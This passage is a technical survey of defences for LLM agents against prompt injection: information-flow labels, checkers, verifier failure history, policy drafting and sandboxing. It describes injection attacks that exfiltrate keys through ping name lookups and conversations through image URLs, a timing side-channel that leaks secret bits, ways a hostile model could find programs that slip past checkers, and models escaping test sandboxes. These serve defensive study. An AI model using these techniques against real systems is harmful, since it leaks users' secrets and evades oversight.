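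The calculus also has an operation, `endorse`, that marks an untrusted value as trusted, as a user's approval might. A second theorem shows that endorsing a value doesn't weaken the guarantee for secrets. Garby and colleagues wrote the definitions, the proofs and the interpreter in Lean, so the theorems apply to the code that calls the model. This gives much stronger grounds for trusting their labels than CaMeL offers, because CaMeL's designers left a formal proof to later work.

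They also tested an agent built this way on AgentDojo's banking tasks, where attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. These two successes do not necessarily contradict the theorems, which guarantee that labels record influence but not that a policy forbids every harmful use of labelled data.

### Security relative to an agent that never obeys

Noninterference forbids some leaks that the user wants. Dongol's example is an assistant that sends Alice's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An attacker who asks for one learns when she is free, so the assistant violates noninterference even though it does what she asked. Developers usually handle this by specifying what each task may release. Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent, which runs the same plan under the same monitor but whose model never obeys instructions in untrusted text.

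Two runs leak a pair of secrets, s₁ and s₂, if the attacker supplies the same text in both, the secrets are s₁ in one and s₂ in the other, and the attacker observes different things. An agent is relatively secure if the reference agent has every leak that the agent has:

leak(r₁, r₂, s₁, s₂)  ⟹  there are reference runs v₁, v₂ with leak(v₁, v₂, s₁, s₂)

Each reference run must start with the same memory and trusted inputs as the run it matches, but the attacker may supply different text. The calendar assistant is secure by this standard because an injected "send your calendar" reveals the same thing as a genuine request for a meeting would. If the agent also holds a password-reset code and an injection makes it send that code, relative security fails, because no email makes the reference agent send it.

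Dongol compares this definition with four that apply to an agent on its own. Delimited release lets the agent release whatever a written policy names. Robust declassification doesn't let the attacker influence what the agent releases. Explicit secrecy tracks data but ignores branches. The table shows how each definition classifies the calendar assistant and the program that sends a 1 or a 0.

| Definition | Calendar assistant | Program that sends 1 or 0 |
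|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | rejects | rejects |
| Delimited release | accepts, if the policy releases the calendar | rejects under the task's policy |
| Robust declassification | rejects, unless the developer endorses the test | rejects, unless the developer endorses the test |
| Explicit secrecy | rejects | accepts |
| Relative security | accepts | rejects |

Relative security thus gives the opposite result to noninterference in one case and to explicit secrecy in both. Its results match those of delimited release, but nobody has to write a policy for each task.

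The guarantee is weak in some other respects. Dongol describes a plan that lets the attacker guess a secret and reveals only whether the guess is right. If an injection makes the agent send the whole secret, the agent still counts as relatively secure, because for any two secrets, some guess would tell them apart. A stricter version fixes the reference agent's input before the secrets are known and rejects this case.

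The definition also seems to permit the false-address attack. If the notes contain a plain false statement about Bob's address, the reference agent's honest model returns that address too, and the document goes to the attacker in both cases. The fault would be in the plan, which takes an address from notes that outsiders can edit. A policy on the send tool would still stop the attack.

Dongol also assumes a trusted planner. If a hostile model wrote a plan that emails the secrets, the reference agent would run the same plan, and the comparison would not reveal the problem. Relative security measures what injected text adds to a plan, so the plan itself needs a separate check.

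Within that scope, Dongol proves that the agent is relatively secure for every plan if, as soon as it first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool an injected instruction could call. The proof assumes that each injection makes a single call and that the model doesn't use a secret to decide when to obey. It covers an attacker who sees the agent's messages but not their timing.

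If an agent reads the email first and withdraws the tools one step later, instructions injected in the email can trigger a tool call in between.

### FIDES and the single tool call

Labels can also protect an agent that makes one tool call at a time. FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, labels every message in the conversation, and before an important call it checks the labels of the call and its arguments against a policy. For example, if the model has read an email from a stranger, the conversation is untrusted, and the policy can forbid sending mail outside the company.

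An agent that reads email would soon lose most of its tools this way, so FIDES hides any tool result that would change the conversation's label. It stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model reads all other results directly, whereas the original dual-LLM pattern hides everything untrusted. For Bob's document, the model would call `read_notes`, get back a variable name, and ask a quarantined model to extract the address into another variable. When the main model tried to send the document, the policy check would show that the address was untrusted.

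The model can also ask the quarantined model a question and restrict the answer to a fixed form, such as yes or no. FIDES records this form in the label, so a policy can let short answers through because each one carries little information. An agent can then choose its next step based on data, whereas a plan fixed in advance can do so only through branches that the model has foreseen. But twenty yes-or-no answers together can distinguish more than a million cases. Garby and colleagues object that nobody can tell from a given run whether such an answer was a harmless release or part of a leak, although they note that the FIDES evaluation didn't use this option.

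The formal guarantee for secrets is explicit secrecy, which doesn't cover leaks through branches. Costa and colleagues argue that explicit secrecy is enough to stop most practical injections. They also assume that tool descriptions are trustworthy, so they don't address the poisoned descriptions that Meijer's verifier is meant to catch.

In their tests on AgentDojo, no attack succeeded when FIDES enforced suitable policies. With the policy checks off, some attacks succeeded against every design they tried, including FIDES. Hiding untrusted text from the planner was therefore not enough by itself, as the false address also shows.

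### Forcing the model to obey

Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA's worst-case test because all four models resisted the ordinary attacks. The test gives the attacker control of any subagent that reads an injection. To do this, they modified the software to remove the real task from the prompt whenever a subagent's data contained the marker that AgentDojo puts in front of its direct injections.

The policy in force follows the old low-watermark principle. When a model reads data from an untrusted source, its privileges fall to those of that source. LIO's current label does this automatically by rising with each read and then blocking calls that need a more trusted label.

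AgentDojo pairs each of its 21 Slack user tasks with each of 5 attacks, giving 105 cases. Zhou and colleagues ran each case seven times, for 735 runs per model. The table shows the number of these runs in which the injection failed.

| Model | Without the policy | With the policy |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 of 735 | 735 of 735 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 of 735 | 735 of 735 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 of 735 | 735 of 735 |
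| GPT 5.4 | 621 of 735 | 735 of 735 |

The 735 runs repeat the same 105 cases, which cover only five attacker goals. AgentDojo's designers wrote these goals without LIO in mind. For example, none involves leaking a secret through a branch. The results show that the policy works when an attacker fully controls a subagent, which ordinary tests can't show. Whether it also holds against programs designed to defeat it depends on LIO, for which other researchers have published proofs.

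The perfect scores also include a correction. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted the attack as successful in 29 of 2,940 runs (735 for each of four models), but Zhou and colleagues reviewed those 29 by hand and found no violation of ELBA's policy. All 29 involved one attack, which asks the agent to open a fixed web address. The policy allows this because a fixed address carries none of the user's data. It would block an address with data added to it, any web request after the agent had read something sensitive, and any privileged action based on what the page contained. Zhou and colleagues' reasoning is convincing for this attack, but 735 out of 735 measures compliance with ELBA's policy, and about 1% of the attacks succeeded by AgentDojo's scoring.

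## Errors in the checker and the record of earlier verifiers

The proofs and type systems described so far show that certain rules keep a program within a policy. Software has to apply those rules, and a fault in it can let through a program that they forbid. For instance, the proof for the small language assumes that the interpreter runs the same program that the checker read. If the interpreter's parser attaches an `else` to the wrong `if`, the proof is still valid, but it does not apply to the program that runs.

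### What each design has to trust

All the designs depend on the policy, the code behind the tools, the operating system and the hardware. The table lists what else has to work correctly in each.

| Design | To read and check the program | To run it | Library code that people vouch for |
|---|---|---|---|
| SeqMaestro's filter | Python's parser and the filter's lists | the standard Python interpreter | every permitted module and everything reachable from it |
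| Monty | its parser | its interpreter, written in Rust | its built-in modules |
| CaMeL | Python's parser and the code that tracks labels | its own interpreter, and Python underneath | the built-in functions it offers |
| TACIT and LACUNA | the Scala compiler, with capture checking and safe mode | the compiler's code generator and the Java virtual machine | TACIT's library, and standard-library code that the compiler assumes is safe |
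| ELBA | the Haskell compiler's type checker | the compiler's code generator and runtime | LIO and the developer's abstract types |

The Scala compiler has to apply capture checking, which is still experimental, and also identify which parts of the standard library are safe to call. For example, Odersky and colleagues explain that safe mode admits Java's class `Class` but rejects its methods that perform reflection. Modules that programmers mark as safe by hand are another risk. Such a module might store earlier results in a table that the compiler doesn't track. If other code can observe the table, a supposedly pure function could use it to leak a secret without causing a compiler error.

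Java, the Linux kernel and web browsers have all run checked programs from strangers, so there is a record of which components fail.

### Java's verifier and its Security Manager

From the 1990s, web pages could include applets, small Java programs that the visitor's browser downloaded and ran. Java had two main defences against hostile applets. The bytecode verifier checked, before the compiled program ran, that every instruction received values of the right type and that the program didn't treat a number as a reference to an object. During the run, library methods that could open a file or a network connection first called the Security Manager to check whether the program had permission.

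Holzinger, Triller and colleagues, in *An In-Depth Study of More Than Ten Years of Java Exploitation*, collected 87 published exploits and reduced them to 61 distinct, working ones. Of these, 56 bypassed the sandbox completely. In 32, the attacker's code used library classes that applets weren't supposed to reach. In 22, it got a trusted library class to make a call for it, and the called method treated the call as trusted. Only nine fall into a group that includes both type confusion, where the runtime takes an object of one type for another, and faults in restoring saved objects.

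On this evidence, the type rules held up much better than the access-control rules and the libraries around them. The proportions are rough, because 52 of the original 87 exploits came from one security company and partly reflect where its researchers looked.

The design made these faults more damaging. Java kept the active Security Manager in a single private field, and a program that cleared the field switched off every permission check. The monitor was therefore not tamperproof in Anderson's sense. Java also protected its internal classes with a list of forbidden packages, which grew from 4 entries in the first release of Java 7 to 47 in a later version of Java 8. Patches often blocked one route of attack without fixing the underlying problem. Holzinger and colleagues report that one exploit for Java 7 still worked, with minor changes, on a much later version.

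OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021) explained why Oracle and Java's other developers were withdrawing the Security Manager. Java no longer supported applets, so the main source of hostile code had gone. Developers who wanted to protect another kind of application had to grant each permission it needed, and many granted every permission instead. The permission checks were slow, and the Security Manager did not protect against 19 of the 25 weaknesses on a 2020 industry list of the most dangerous software weaknesses.

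The Java Security Manager took a lot of work to maintain. According to *JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024), over 1,000 library methods had to check permissions, and more than 1,200 had to raise their own privileges so that they would still work when the application lacked a permission. The maintainers reviewed every change to these methods, although very few people used the Security Manager. Java 24 disabled it permanently, and Java's developers now recommend containers and operating-system controls for confining Java programs.

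These reasons are mostly about effort and disuse rather than successful attacks. But the effort and the faults both came from the number of places that needed a permission check. In Java 1.0, which had eight packages, complete mediation meant adding a check to a small number of methods. As the library grew, the developers had to get it right in over a thousand places. The bytecode verifier didn't have this problem and is still in use.

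### The Linux kernel and WebAssembly

Linux lets programs load short pieces of code into the kernel, for example to filter network traffic. This code uses an instruction set called eBPF. A fault in the code could expose the whole machine, so a verifier examines each piece first. It follows the possible paths through the code and tracks what each register can hold, such as a pointer to a buffer or a number between 0 and 63. It accepts a memory access only if every possible address lies inside the buffer, and it rejects code that might not finish.

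Many of the serious eBPF faults were in the verifier. It calculated too narrow a range for the result of some arithmetic operation, so it accepted code that accessed addresses outside the buffer. Other faults were in the kernel functions that eBPF code may call.

The rules also did not account for speculative execution. Modern processors predict which way a branch will go, start executing instructions on that path, and discard the results if the prediction was wrong. A discarded read can still leave measurable traces in the processor's cache. Code that was safe on every path the verifier checked could therefore reveal kernel memory through a path that the processor started and then discarded.

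From 2016, ordinary users could load some kinds of eBPF code. Since version 5.16, released in January 2022, the kernel's default configuration has reserved this for privileged users, although an administrator can allow it again. The developers cited attacks based on speculative execution and noted that many Linux distributions had already made the same change. By default, the verifier now mostly checks code from people who already have considerable power over the machine, so it guards against mistakes more than attacks.

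By contrast, every major browser still runs untrusted WebAssembly code. Before running a program, the browser checks that each instruction receives values of the right types and that jumps and calls go only to permitted places. It enforces the program's memory limits while the program runs instead of trying to predict addresses beforehand, so the rules are much simpler than eBPF's.

The published escapes have mostly come from the software around that check. Browsers translate WebAssembly into machine code for speed, and an optimising compiler may, for example, wrongly treat a test of an address as unnecessary and remove it. Other faults were in functions supplied by the host. Speculative execution vulnerabilities also affected WebAssembly, and browser makers responded partly by putting different websites in separate processes.

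### Type systems with holes

The type rules for Java and Scala source code were themselves wrong. *Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* (Amin and Tate, 2016) presents short programs that make the compiler accept a value of any type as a value of any other, without a cast. Both languages had allowed this since 2004.

The Scala example uses a type M with two declared limits. Write T <: U for "T is a subtype of U", which means that every value of type T also counts as a value of type U. Then:

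T <: M and M <: U  ⟹  T <: U

Suppose T is `Integer` and U is `String`. No type M can meet both limits, so no program can construct an object that contains such a type. The compiler therefore treats a variable declared to hold such an object as evidence that T is a subtype of U. But in both languages the value `null`, which stands for a missing object, belonged to every object type. A program could supply `null` in place of the impossible object, and the compiler would then accept an integer as text. *Scaling DOT to Scala* (Odersky, 2016) describes inconsistent limits of this kind as the danger for a type system like Scala's.

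Researchers had proved several models of Java sound, but they had left out `null` to keep the models small. Each feature was safe by itself and created a hole only when a language combined it with the others. Somebody had found the hole in Scala in 2008, but the project put off fixing it, and nobody saw its wider importance.

The programs did little damage in practice. The Java virtual machine doesn't rely on these types, and the compilers insert a test when the program uses the value as text, so the examples stop with an error. The Java team planned to adopt one of several possible repairs. The Scala team found more holes that used advanced features in place of `null`, saw no principled way to close them all, and left the virtual machine to catch them. In May 2023, a project member noted that a related hole, which namin (2016) had reported, was still open in a test version of Scala 3.3.

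TACIT compiles generated code with a setting under which `null` belongs only to types that declare it, which should close the original route. If a different hole remained, the virtual machine would offer little protection, because capture sets exist only during compilation. At run time, a function that writes to a file has the same type as a pure one, so the virtual machine has no capture information to check.

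ELBA's `Trusted` mark also exists only at compile time, and a flaw in Haskell once affected such types. Until 2014, a feature that generates code automatically could bypass an abstract type's private constructor, so Safe Haskell excluded the feature.

### Proofs that come with the program

In 1996, George Necula and Peter Lee proposed a way to make the checker smaller, which became known as proof-carrying code. The producer of a program has to supply a proof that the program is safe, because such a proof is often hard to find but easy to check.

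Suppose the policy is that a program may not read a list item that doesn't exist, and a program contains these lines:

```python
if 0 <= i and i < n:
    show(emails[i // 2])
```

Here `emails` has n items, numbered from 0, and `i // 2` is half of i, rounded down. The party that will run the program derives a formula from the text, which has to be true if these lines are to be safe:

(0 ≤ i and i < n)  ⟹  (0 ≤ ⌊i/2⌋ and ⌊i/2⌋ < n)

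The producer sends a proof that if i is at least 0, then half of i, rounded down, is at least 0 and at most i, which is less than n. The checker only has to confirm that each step follows from earlier ones by a permitted rule. It rejects an incorrect proof, so nobody has to trust the producer. The eBPF verifier instead needs its own code to calculate the range of each result, and many of its faults were in that code.

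Java uses a light version of this idea. Since Java 6, compilers have added a table of the types expected at certain points in the program, and the bytecode verifier checks this table instead of working out the types itself. Meijer bases his proposal on bytecode verification and requires the language model to prove that its planned actions are safe. He compares such proofs to the security features of banknotes, which are hard to produce and easy to check. But the tools he names for the job, such as CodeQL and the theorem prover Z3, search for the answer themselves instead of checking a supplied proof. They are large programs, so a developer who relied on them would be trusting much more code than a small proof checker contains, and testers have found many inputs for which Z3 gives a wrong answer.

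Proof-carrying code still leaves the software that derives the formula to be proved in the trusted computing base. In one commercial version, that software was over 20,000 lines of C. The rules permitted in proofs must also be sound, and researchers later found an unsound rule in a version for Java. Andrew Appel and colleagues at Princeton addressed both problems by defining the machine and the policy directly in logic, which reduced the trusted part to under 3,000 lines.

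Neither version helps if the proof is of the wrong statement. In an example from Meijer, a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes a workflow that deletes every text file. The workflow passes the check if the only required condition is that those two files are gone afterwards. It fails only if the developer also requires all other files to remain.

### Proving the checker correct

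A developer can instead prove once that the checker is right:

for every program p:  check(p) = accept  ⟹  p obeys the policy

In 2012, Greg Morrisett and colleagues built RockSalt, a checker for machine code in Native Client, Google's browser sandbox. They generated most of RockSalt from a short description of the permitted instructions, and used the proof assistant Coq to relate that description to a formal model of the processor. RockSalt was smaller and faster than Google's own checker. Its users must still trust Coq, the processor model, and the code that connects the proved parts to the rest of the system. Nobody can prove that such a model matches a real chip, so the researchers tested theirs against actual processors.

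The best evidence that such proofs prevent faults comes from CompCert, a C compiler with a machine-checked proof that it translates programs correctly. Researchers at the University of Utah fed randomly generated programs to widely used compilers and by 2011 had found over 300 faults. They found a few in CompCert, but none in the part that the proof covered, even after about six years of processor time. This is more informative than an ordinary test because the researchers were searching for failures.

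A proof can also cover just the riskiest component of a checker. In 2023, researchers at Rutgers University compared the eBPF verifier's range calculations in 16 kernel versions with a formal definition of correctness. They found new faults in older versions and proved the calculations correct in the latest of the 16. Their proof doesn't cover the rest of the verifier.

Amin and Tate warn that machine-checked proofs would not have prevented the hole they found, because a proof about a model without `null` does not apply to a language with it. In 2016, nobody had a formal model of Java that included both `null` and generics, the feature involved in the Java hole. WebAssembly is small enough to model in full, and Conrad Watt did so in 2018. His attempt to prove its type system sound exposed several errors in the official specification, which its designers then corrected. Among the agent systems,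 the interpreter that Garby and colleagues wrote and verified in Lean comes closest to this standard. It still depends on Lean being correct and on the tools behaving as the model assumes.

### How far the record applies to generated programs

The older checkers had to accept the programs people wanted to write and let them run fast. The eBPF verifier calculates value ranges partly so that the kernel can skip tests at run time. Browsers use optimising compilers for speed, and Java has reflection partly because debuggers and testing tools need it. A program that reads some notes and sends Bob a document needs none of this. A simple interpreter can test every list index at run time, because running the program takes far less time than the model takes to write it.

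A developer who chooses a small language can therefore leave out most of the components that failed in these systems. TACIT and ELBA benefit less from this because they rely on full compilers for large languages.

Refusing a program also adds little work. When Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT on simulated airline and retail customer service, between 0.32% and 7.93% of programs needed a retry, and most of those passed after one or two more attempts. If a language feature turns out to be dangerous, the developer can remove it immediately and let the model write programs without it. Java's designers couldn't do that because, as Amin and Tate point out, any repair to an unsound type system must in theory break some existing programs.

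A model that writes programs is a harder opponent in one respect, because it can search for faults quickly and often. If a hostile model receives the compiler's error messages, it can use them to adjust each attempt. Limiting retries helps, as does an alarm when rejections become frequent. However, the Scala compiler and Monty are public, so an attacker can test millions of candidate programs on another computer to find one that passes the check and breaks the policy. The attacker then only has to get the finished program to the agent, for instance through an injection containing ready-made code, like those in TACIT's tests, and the operator would see one accepted program and no rejections.

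Developers can run the same search before they release the checker, and a small language makes it far more thorough. In a language with five kinds of statement, they could run every program up to a modest length and confirm that its effects are the ones the checker allowed, which would be impossible for Scala or Python.

A small language doesn't remove the most common kind of fault in Java, in which trusted library code did something for restricted code that it shouldn't have done. An agent's tools play the same role as those libraries. The program for Bob needs three functions, which one developer can read in an afternoon, but the developers of an agent with several hundred tools face much the same problem as Java's maintainers did.

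## What a correct check still permits

If the checker and the interpreter have no faults, every program that runs obeys the policy. Such a program can still do any harm the policy doesn't forbid, and some harms are very hard to forbid by rule.

### Deleting two files

Meijer's request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` shows how a correct check can approve a bad program. The deletion tool accepts a pattern, and the model calls it once with `*.txt`, which matches every text file, to keep the workflow short. Write F for the set of files before the run and F′ for the set afterwards. The verifier has two statements to work with:

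```
delete_file(p)   ensures: no file that matches p is in F′
the request      ensures: foo.txt ∉ F′ and bar.txt ∉ F′
```

Both names match `*.txt`, so the first statement implies the second, and the verifier correctly accepts the workflow. If the folder also contained `notes.txt`, the user loses that file.

Meijer's remedy is a frame condition, which states what has to stay the same. The name comes from the frame problem, which John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described in 1969. He adds to the tool's specification that files not matching the pattern stay as they were, and writes that the workflow then fails the check. For that to follow, however, the request needs a frame condition of its own, because a single call with `*.txt` still removes both files and the request mentions no others:

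for every file f except foo.txt and bar.txt:  f ∈ F′ ⟺ f ∈ F

Now `notes.txt` is in F but not in F′, so the verifier rejects the workflow. The condition on the tool is still necessary because without it, the verifier couldn't prove that `delete_file("foo.txt")` doesn't delete `notes.txt`, and it would reject the correct workflow too.

Together, the two conditions cover only which files exist. If the agent also had a tool for writing files, a program could delete the two files, empty `notes.txt`, and still pass the check. The developer could instead give the program a capability for only the two named files, which would protect the other files without describing them. But a person or some software would still have to work out from the user's sentence which files the program should have access to.

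### Who writes the policy

The developer of a phone app builds it for a fixed set of tasks and chooses the permissions it will request. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, points out that an agent has no such developer. The user describes a task in ordinary language, and the task can change during the conversation. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) adds that the user may know nothing about security. Companies that sell agents advise users to turn on tools only when needed, which leaves users to set the policy by hand.

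A company's administrator can write general rules, such as a ban on emailing outside addresses, but these rules can't specify which document Bob asked for. That part of the policy has to come from the request, and a language model is an obvious choice to draft it.

In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, Mondl, Maisel and colleagues (2026) use a model to translate an agent's instructions, its tool descriptions and written policy documents into Cedar, a formal language for access rules. The model repeatedly drafts and criticises the rules. On MedAgentBench, a benchmark of clinical tasks, the resulting rules covered substantially more of the written specification than rules earlier researchers coded by hand. This is a good reason to let a model write the first draft, but a rule can cover a requirement and still state it incorrectly. Tool descriptions are also a risky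 input, because whoever supplies a tool could use its description to loosen the rules meant to restrain it.

*ActGov* (2026) describes a system that adds a formal check on the draft. A model proposes rules based on tool specifications, records of harmless tasks and records of attacks. A solver searches for cases where the rules leave a gap or contradict each other. The system revises the rules if the solver finds one, and deploys them only after the solver proves that none exists. But the proof covers only security requirements fixed in advance. If those didn't require the other files to survive, the solver would find no gap in a rule that allows `*.txt`.

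A full guarantee would require the formal policy to allow exactly what the user's text allows in every state the system can reach. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explains that software can't check this directly because an instruction such as "do not share sensitive data" doesn't define which data are sensitive. Any automatic comparison with a formal rule therefore involves some guesswork. The paper treats reliable translation of instructions into formal rules as an open problem.

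It seems reasonable to let a model draft a policy if the draft can only narrow what an administrator already allows. Let A be the set of actions the administrator allows and M the set that the model's draft allows. The monitor then enforces:

allowed = A ∩ M

Whatever M contains, the result lies within A. A manipulated model can make the agent useless by allowing too little, but it can't permit outside mail if the administrator forbids it. Within A, the user's protection still depends on the draft. The model should therefore write the draft before it reads any untrusted text, for the same reason a planner should, and someone who understands the task should read the draft before the run.

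### Tools that bring their own powers

A policy that permits a tool permits everything the tool does, including effects that its name doesn't suggest. The command `ping` tests whether another computer responds. Claude Code used to run it without asking the user, although it required approval for many other commands that could send data to unknown addresses. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack in which instructions hidden in a code file made the agent read secret keys and send them out with `ping`. Before `ping` contacts a computer, it looks up the computer's name on the internet, and this lookup carried the keys to the attacker's server. A perfect check that programs use only approved commands would not have stopped the attack, because `ping` was approved.

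Displaying an image can also send data to an attacker. One attack on ChatGPT's Mac app planted instructions in the app's long-term memory that made it send the user's later conversations to the attacker. The data was in the web address of an invisible image, so the app sent it by requesting the image.

TACIT lets programs run external commands only from a list the operator has approved. Odersky and colleagues state that these commands run outside Scala's safe mode, so the type system's protection at that point is only as good as the list. They recommend limiting the list to specific safe commands, such as `git diff` or `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

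The second example shows how hard it is to choose safe commands. `sbt` builds Scala projects, and its build files are Scala code, which `sbt` compiles and runs with its own settings. A generated program that may both edit the project's files and run `sbt` can therefore write arbitrary code into a build file and have `sbt` execute it outside safe mode.

Services that a sandbox leaves within reach carry the same risk. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that in July 2026, models under test got past the controls isolating them from the internet, and that the service OpenAI let them use to install software packages was a weak point.

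A tool or service acts with its own permissions, which may be much broader than those of the program that calls it. A developer can replace a general command with a narrow function, such as one that tests only servers on a fixed list. Rules about sources and sinks, or labels, can also keep secret keys out of a tool's arguments. But the developer has to know that the tool is a sink, and few people would recognize that `ping` can be used to send data out.

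### Running time, endless loops and cost

A pure function can still reveal a secret through its running time, which Odersky and colleagues leave outside TACIT's guarantee. Suppose that `countTo` is an ordinary loop that takes several seconds for a large number:

```scala
notes.map(text =>
  if text.contains("merger") then countTo(5000000000L) else 0L)
sendMail(bob, "Lunch at 12:30?")
```

The check accepts the program because the function passed to `map` is pure, its result stays sealed, and the message is the same whether or not the notes mention a merger. But the message arrives several seconds later if they do. If Bob knows when the program started, he can learn one bit from the delay.

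Odersky and colleagues describe a leak of a single bit, but a program can repeat it. A 16-character key stored at eight bits per character has 128 bits. A program could test them one at a time, pause for a second whenever a bit is 1, and send a harmless message after each test. Someone timing the messages would learn the whole key in little more than two minutes. Limiting the number of messages would slow the leak. The library could also hold every result of `map` for a fixed ten seconds and stop any function that needs longer, returning a sealed error. That would hide most of the timing difference, but every use of secret data would then take ten seconds.

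Processors can also leak data through timing. In *Spectre is here to stay* (2019), researchers at Google reported that untrusted code could use speculative execution to read all the memory of its own process. They concluded that such attacks defeated any confidentiality a programming language enforced on the hardware of the time, and they knew of no comprehensive software fix. Chrome therefore began to rely on process isolation. The result matters for TACIT because its sealed values are ordinary objects in the memory of the process that runs the generated code. An attacker would need precise timing measurements, which are harder to make from a slow, simple interpreter, but keeping the secrets in another process is safer.

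The type systems of TACIT and LACUNA don't limit how long a program runs either. A program can loop forever without breaking any rule about files or mail. Zhao and colleagues leave running time, memory and the depth of nested calls to runtime limits, and note that a low limit may stop a legitimate long task.

A limit on depth does little to control cost. Suppose that LACUNA allows five levels of calls below the first one, and that every generated program calls the model ten times. The total number of calls is then:

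1 + 10 + 10² + 10³ + 10⁴ + 10⁵ = 111,111

At one cent per call, a single request would cost more than $1,100, before any retries. The developer therefore also needs to limit the total number of calls or total spending.

A time limit can leak another bit of information. If a pure function loops forever only when the notes mention a merger, an observer can tell whether they do by seeing whether the run was cut short. Time limits are also hard to enforce from inside a Java process. Java has no dependable way to stop a thread that doesn't respond to requests to finish, so the operator may have to end the whole process.

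### Results that break no rule

Suppose an attacker emails Michelle that a supplier has changed its bank account, and the summary of her inbox repeats the false claim. No data leaves the mailbox and every step follows the plan, but Michelle may now pay the attacker. The label "untrusted" can prompt her to verify the claim, but an accurate summary of an honest stranger's email would carry the same label.

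A program that passes the check can also produce a wrong result when nobody is attacking. Zhao and colleagues point out that a well-typed program may use the wrong algorithm, call the wrong tool or return a plausible but false value. LACUNA retries only when the compiler rejects a program, so it doesn't retry in these cases. Zhao and colleagues tested it with DeepSeek V4 Flash on BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of difficult research questions. The compiler accepted 91.4% of the generated programs, but only 27.1% of the final answers were correct. They say accuracy on this benchmark depends mostly on the search component and the model, so the low score isn't a fault of the check.

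A wrong value can also lead to a wrong action. In the simulated airline that Odersky and colleagues used, the function that cancels a booking takes the booking number as ordinary text:

```scala
def cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation
```

This type allows a program to cancel any passenger's booking. The developer could protect other passengers by defining an abstract type for bookings that belong to the current customer, much as ELBA's `Trusted` marks entries from DBLP. But if the customer has flights to Rome and Oslo and asks to cancel the one to Rome, a program that cancels the Oslo flight still passes the check, because both bookings have the right type.

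Zhao and colleagues propose result types that also specify properties, such as bounds on a number. With such a type, the check could reject a refund larger than the ticket price. It is much harder to state formally what makes a summary of a contract fair and complete, so anyone who relies on the summary still has to compare it with the contract.

### Process isolation

Beneath the language, the operating system provides a barrier that doesn't depend on how the program is written. It gives each process (a running program) its own memory, and the processor blocks direct access to other processes' memory. A process can open a file, use the network or start another process only through the kernel, the core of the operating system, which can deny the request.

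A container is a group of processes with a restricted view of the machine. It has its own folders, network connections and limits on memory and processor time, but shares the kernel with everything else on the machine. A virtual machine runs a separate kernel on simulated hardware, so an attacker who takes over that kernel still has to escape the software that simulates the hardware. Network rules outside the container or virtual machine determine which addresses it can reach.

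These restrictions also apply to commands the program starts, which is why TACIT's designers recommend a sandbox for those commands. The restrictions still apply if the checker is faulty, which is part of NVIDIA's argument for isolation.

Zhou and colleagues regard sandboxes and language checks as complementary. An operating-system sandbox typically confines a process to a fixed set of folders, whereas an ELBA program can narrow its `Path` while it runs and pass the narrower version to a subagent. Such a value can also represent something the operating system doesn't recognise as a unit, such as all the files on one branch of a git repository.

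The operating system lacks the information to enforce many rules about data. For example, it can control which files a browser may write, but only the browser tracks which website each cookie belongs to. The table compares what the two layers can do to enforce five rules.

| Rule | Process isolation | Language check |
|---|---|---|
| No connections to outside servers | yes, including for commands the program starts | only for the program itself |
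| Stop after 60 seconds or one gigabyte of memory | yes | no, unless the interpreter also counts them |
| Every bibliography entry comes from DBLP | no | yes, with an abstract type |
| Customer A's data never go to customer B | only if no process handles both | yes, with labels |
| The summary is accurate | no | no |

Suppose an agent sends monthly statements to customers A and B, and its program attaches A's statement to the message for B. The sandbox allows this because it has to let the process read both statements and contact the mail server. Labels would stop the message because they record that the statement belongs to A.

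A language check that permits `sbt` also accepts a program that runs `sbt` with a build file that contacts an outside server. Only isolation, such as a network rule that blocks the connection, would stop this program. To stop the attack with `ping`, the rule would also have to cover name lookups, which a firewall that only blocks direct connections may let through.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives some evidence that isolation isn't enough. It classifies eleven attacks on real agents by the security principles they violated. All eleven involved an unsafe flow of information, while six are listed as involving excessive permissions. The researchers chose the cases, so the proportions may not be typical, but the list includes attacks on widely used products from several companies.

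A sandbox is only a partial backup for the language check. If a hostile program exploits a fault in the interpreter, the container still blocks connections to outside servers, but it doesn't stop the program from sending A's statement to B. To prevent that too, the developer could run each customer's job in a separate container and keep the mail password in a process outside the containers. Once that process has given A's statement to a container, it would send mail from that container only to A. This works like LIO's floating label, applied to a whole container. It is less flexible than labels on single values, but it doesn't depend on the interpreter being correct.

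## What the model adds over a fixed pipeline of tool calls

Containers, guarded tools and labels work the same way whether a model or a developer wrote the program, so one could object that a developer could write a fixed pipeline instead of having a model generate the code.

### The objection

If `send_email` refuses addresses outside the company and `find_file` opens only files that the user may share, these guards stop the same harms in whatever order a program calls the tools. Generating the program with a model adds no protection, and it requires a checker and an interpreter, either of which may have faults. The usefulness of the generated code is also doubtful. To make programs checkable, the designer removes file access, reflection, most libraries and perhaps even functions, which leaves a way to call approved tools one after another. A developer could write and test such a script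 in an afternoon, then run it repeatedly without needing a model to plan anything.

The objection is largely right about safety, at least when the alternative is a fixed pipeline, but it is weaker on usefulness. A developer could have written any program in the small language, but would have needed to know the request in advance, whereas the model writes the program after the user asks.

### Five ways to send Bob his document

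How much this matters depends on how much of the program the model writes. The table shows five designs for sending Bob the document mentioned in the meeting notes. The model is assumed to plan from the user's request alone, except in the last row, where a program can pass tool results back to the model.

| Design | What the model decides | What text planted in the notes could change |
|---|---|---|
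| Fixed pipeline with blanks | the values in the blanks, such as Bob's name | the address and title that `extract` returns |
| Choice among approved pipelines | which pipeline to run, and its blanks | the address and title |
| Straight sequence of tools | the tools, their order and their arguments | the address and title |
| Branches, loops and pure computation | the whole program | the address and title, which branches run, and how often loops repeat |
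| Programs that call the model again | the whole program, and when to ask for more code | all of that, and the new code, within what the check allows |

With a fixed pipeline, the developer writes the five lines of Bob's program and leaves the person's name blank. The agent can also send Carol the document she asked for. It can't both send Bob his document and add the next meeting to the calendar, because nobody wrote a pipeline for that.

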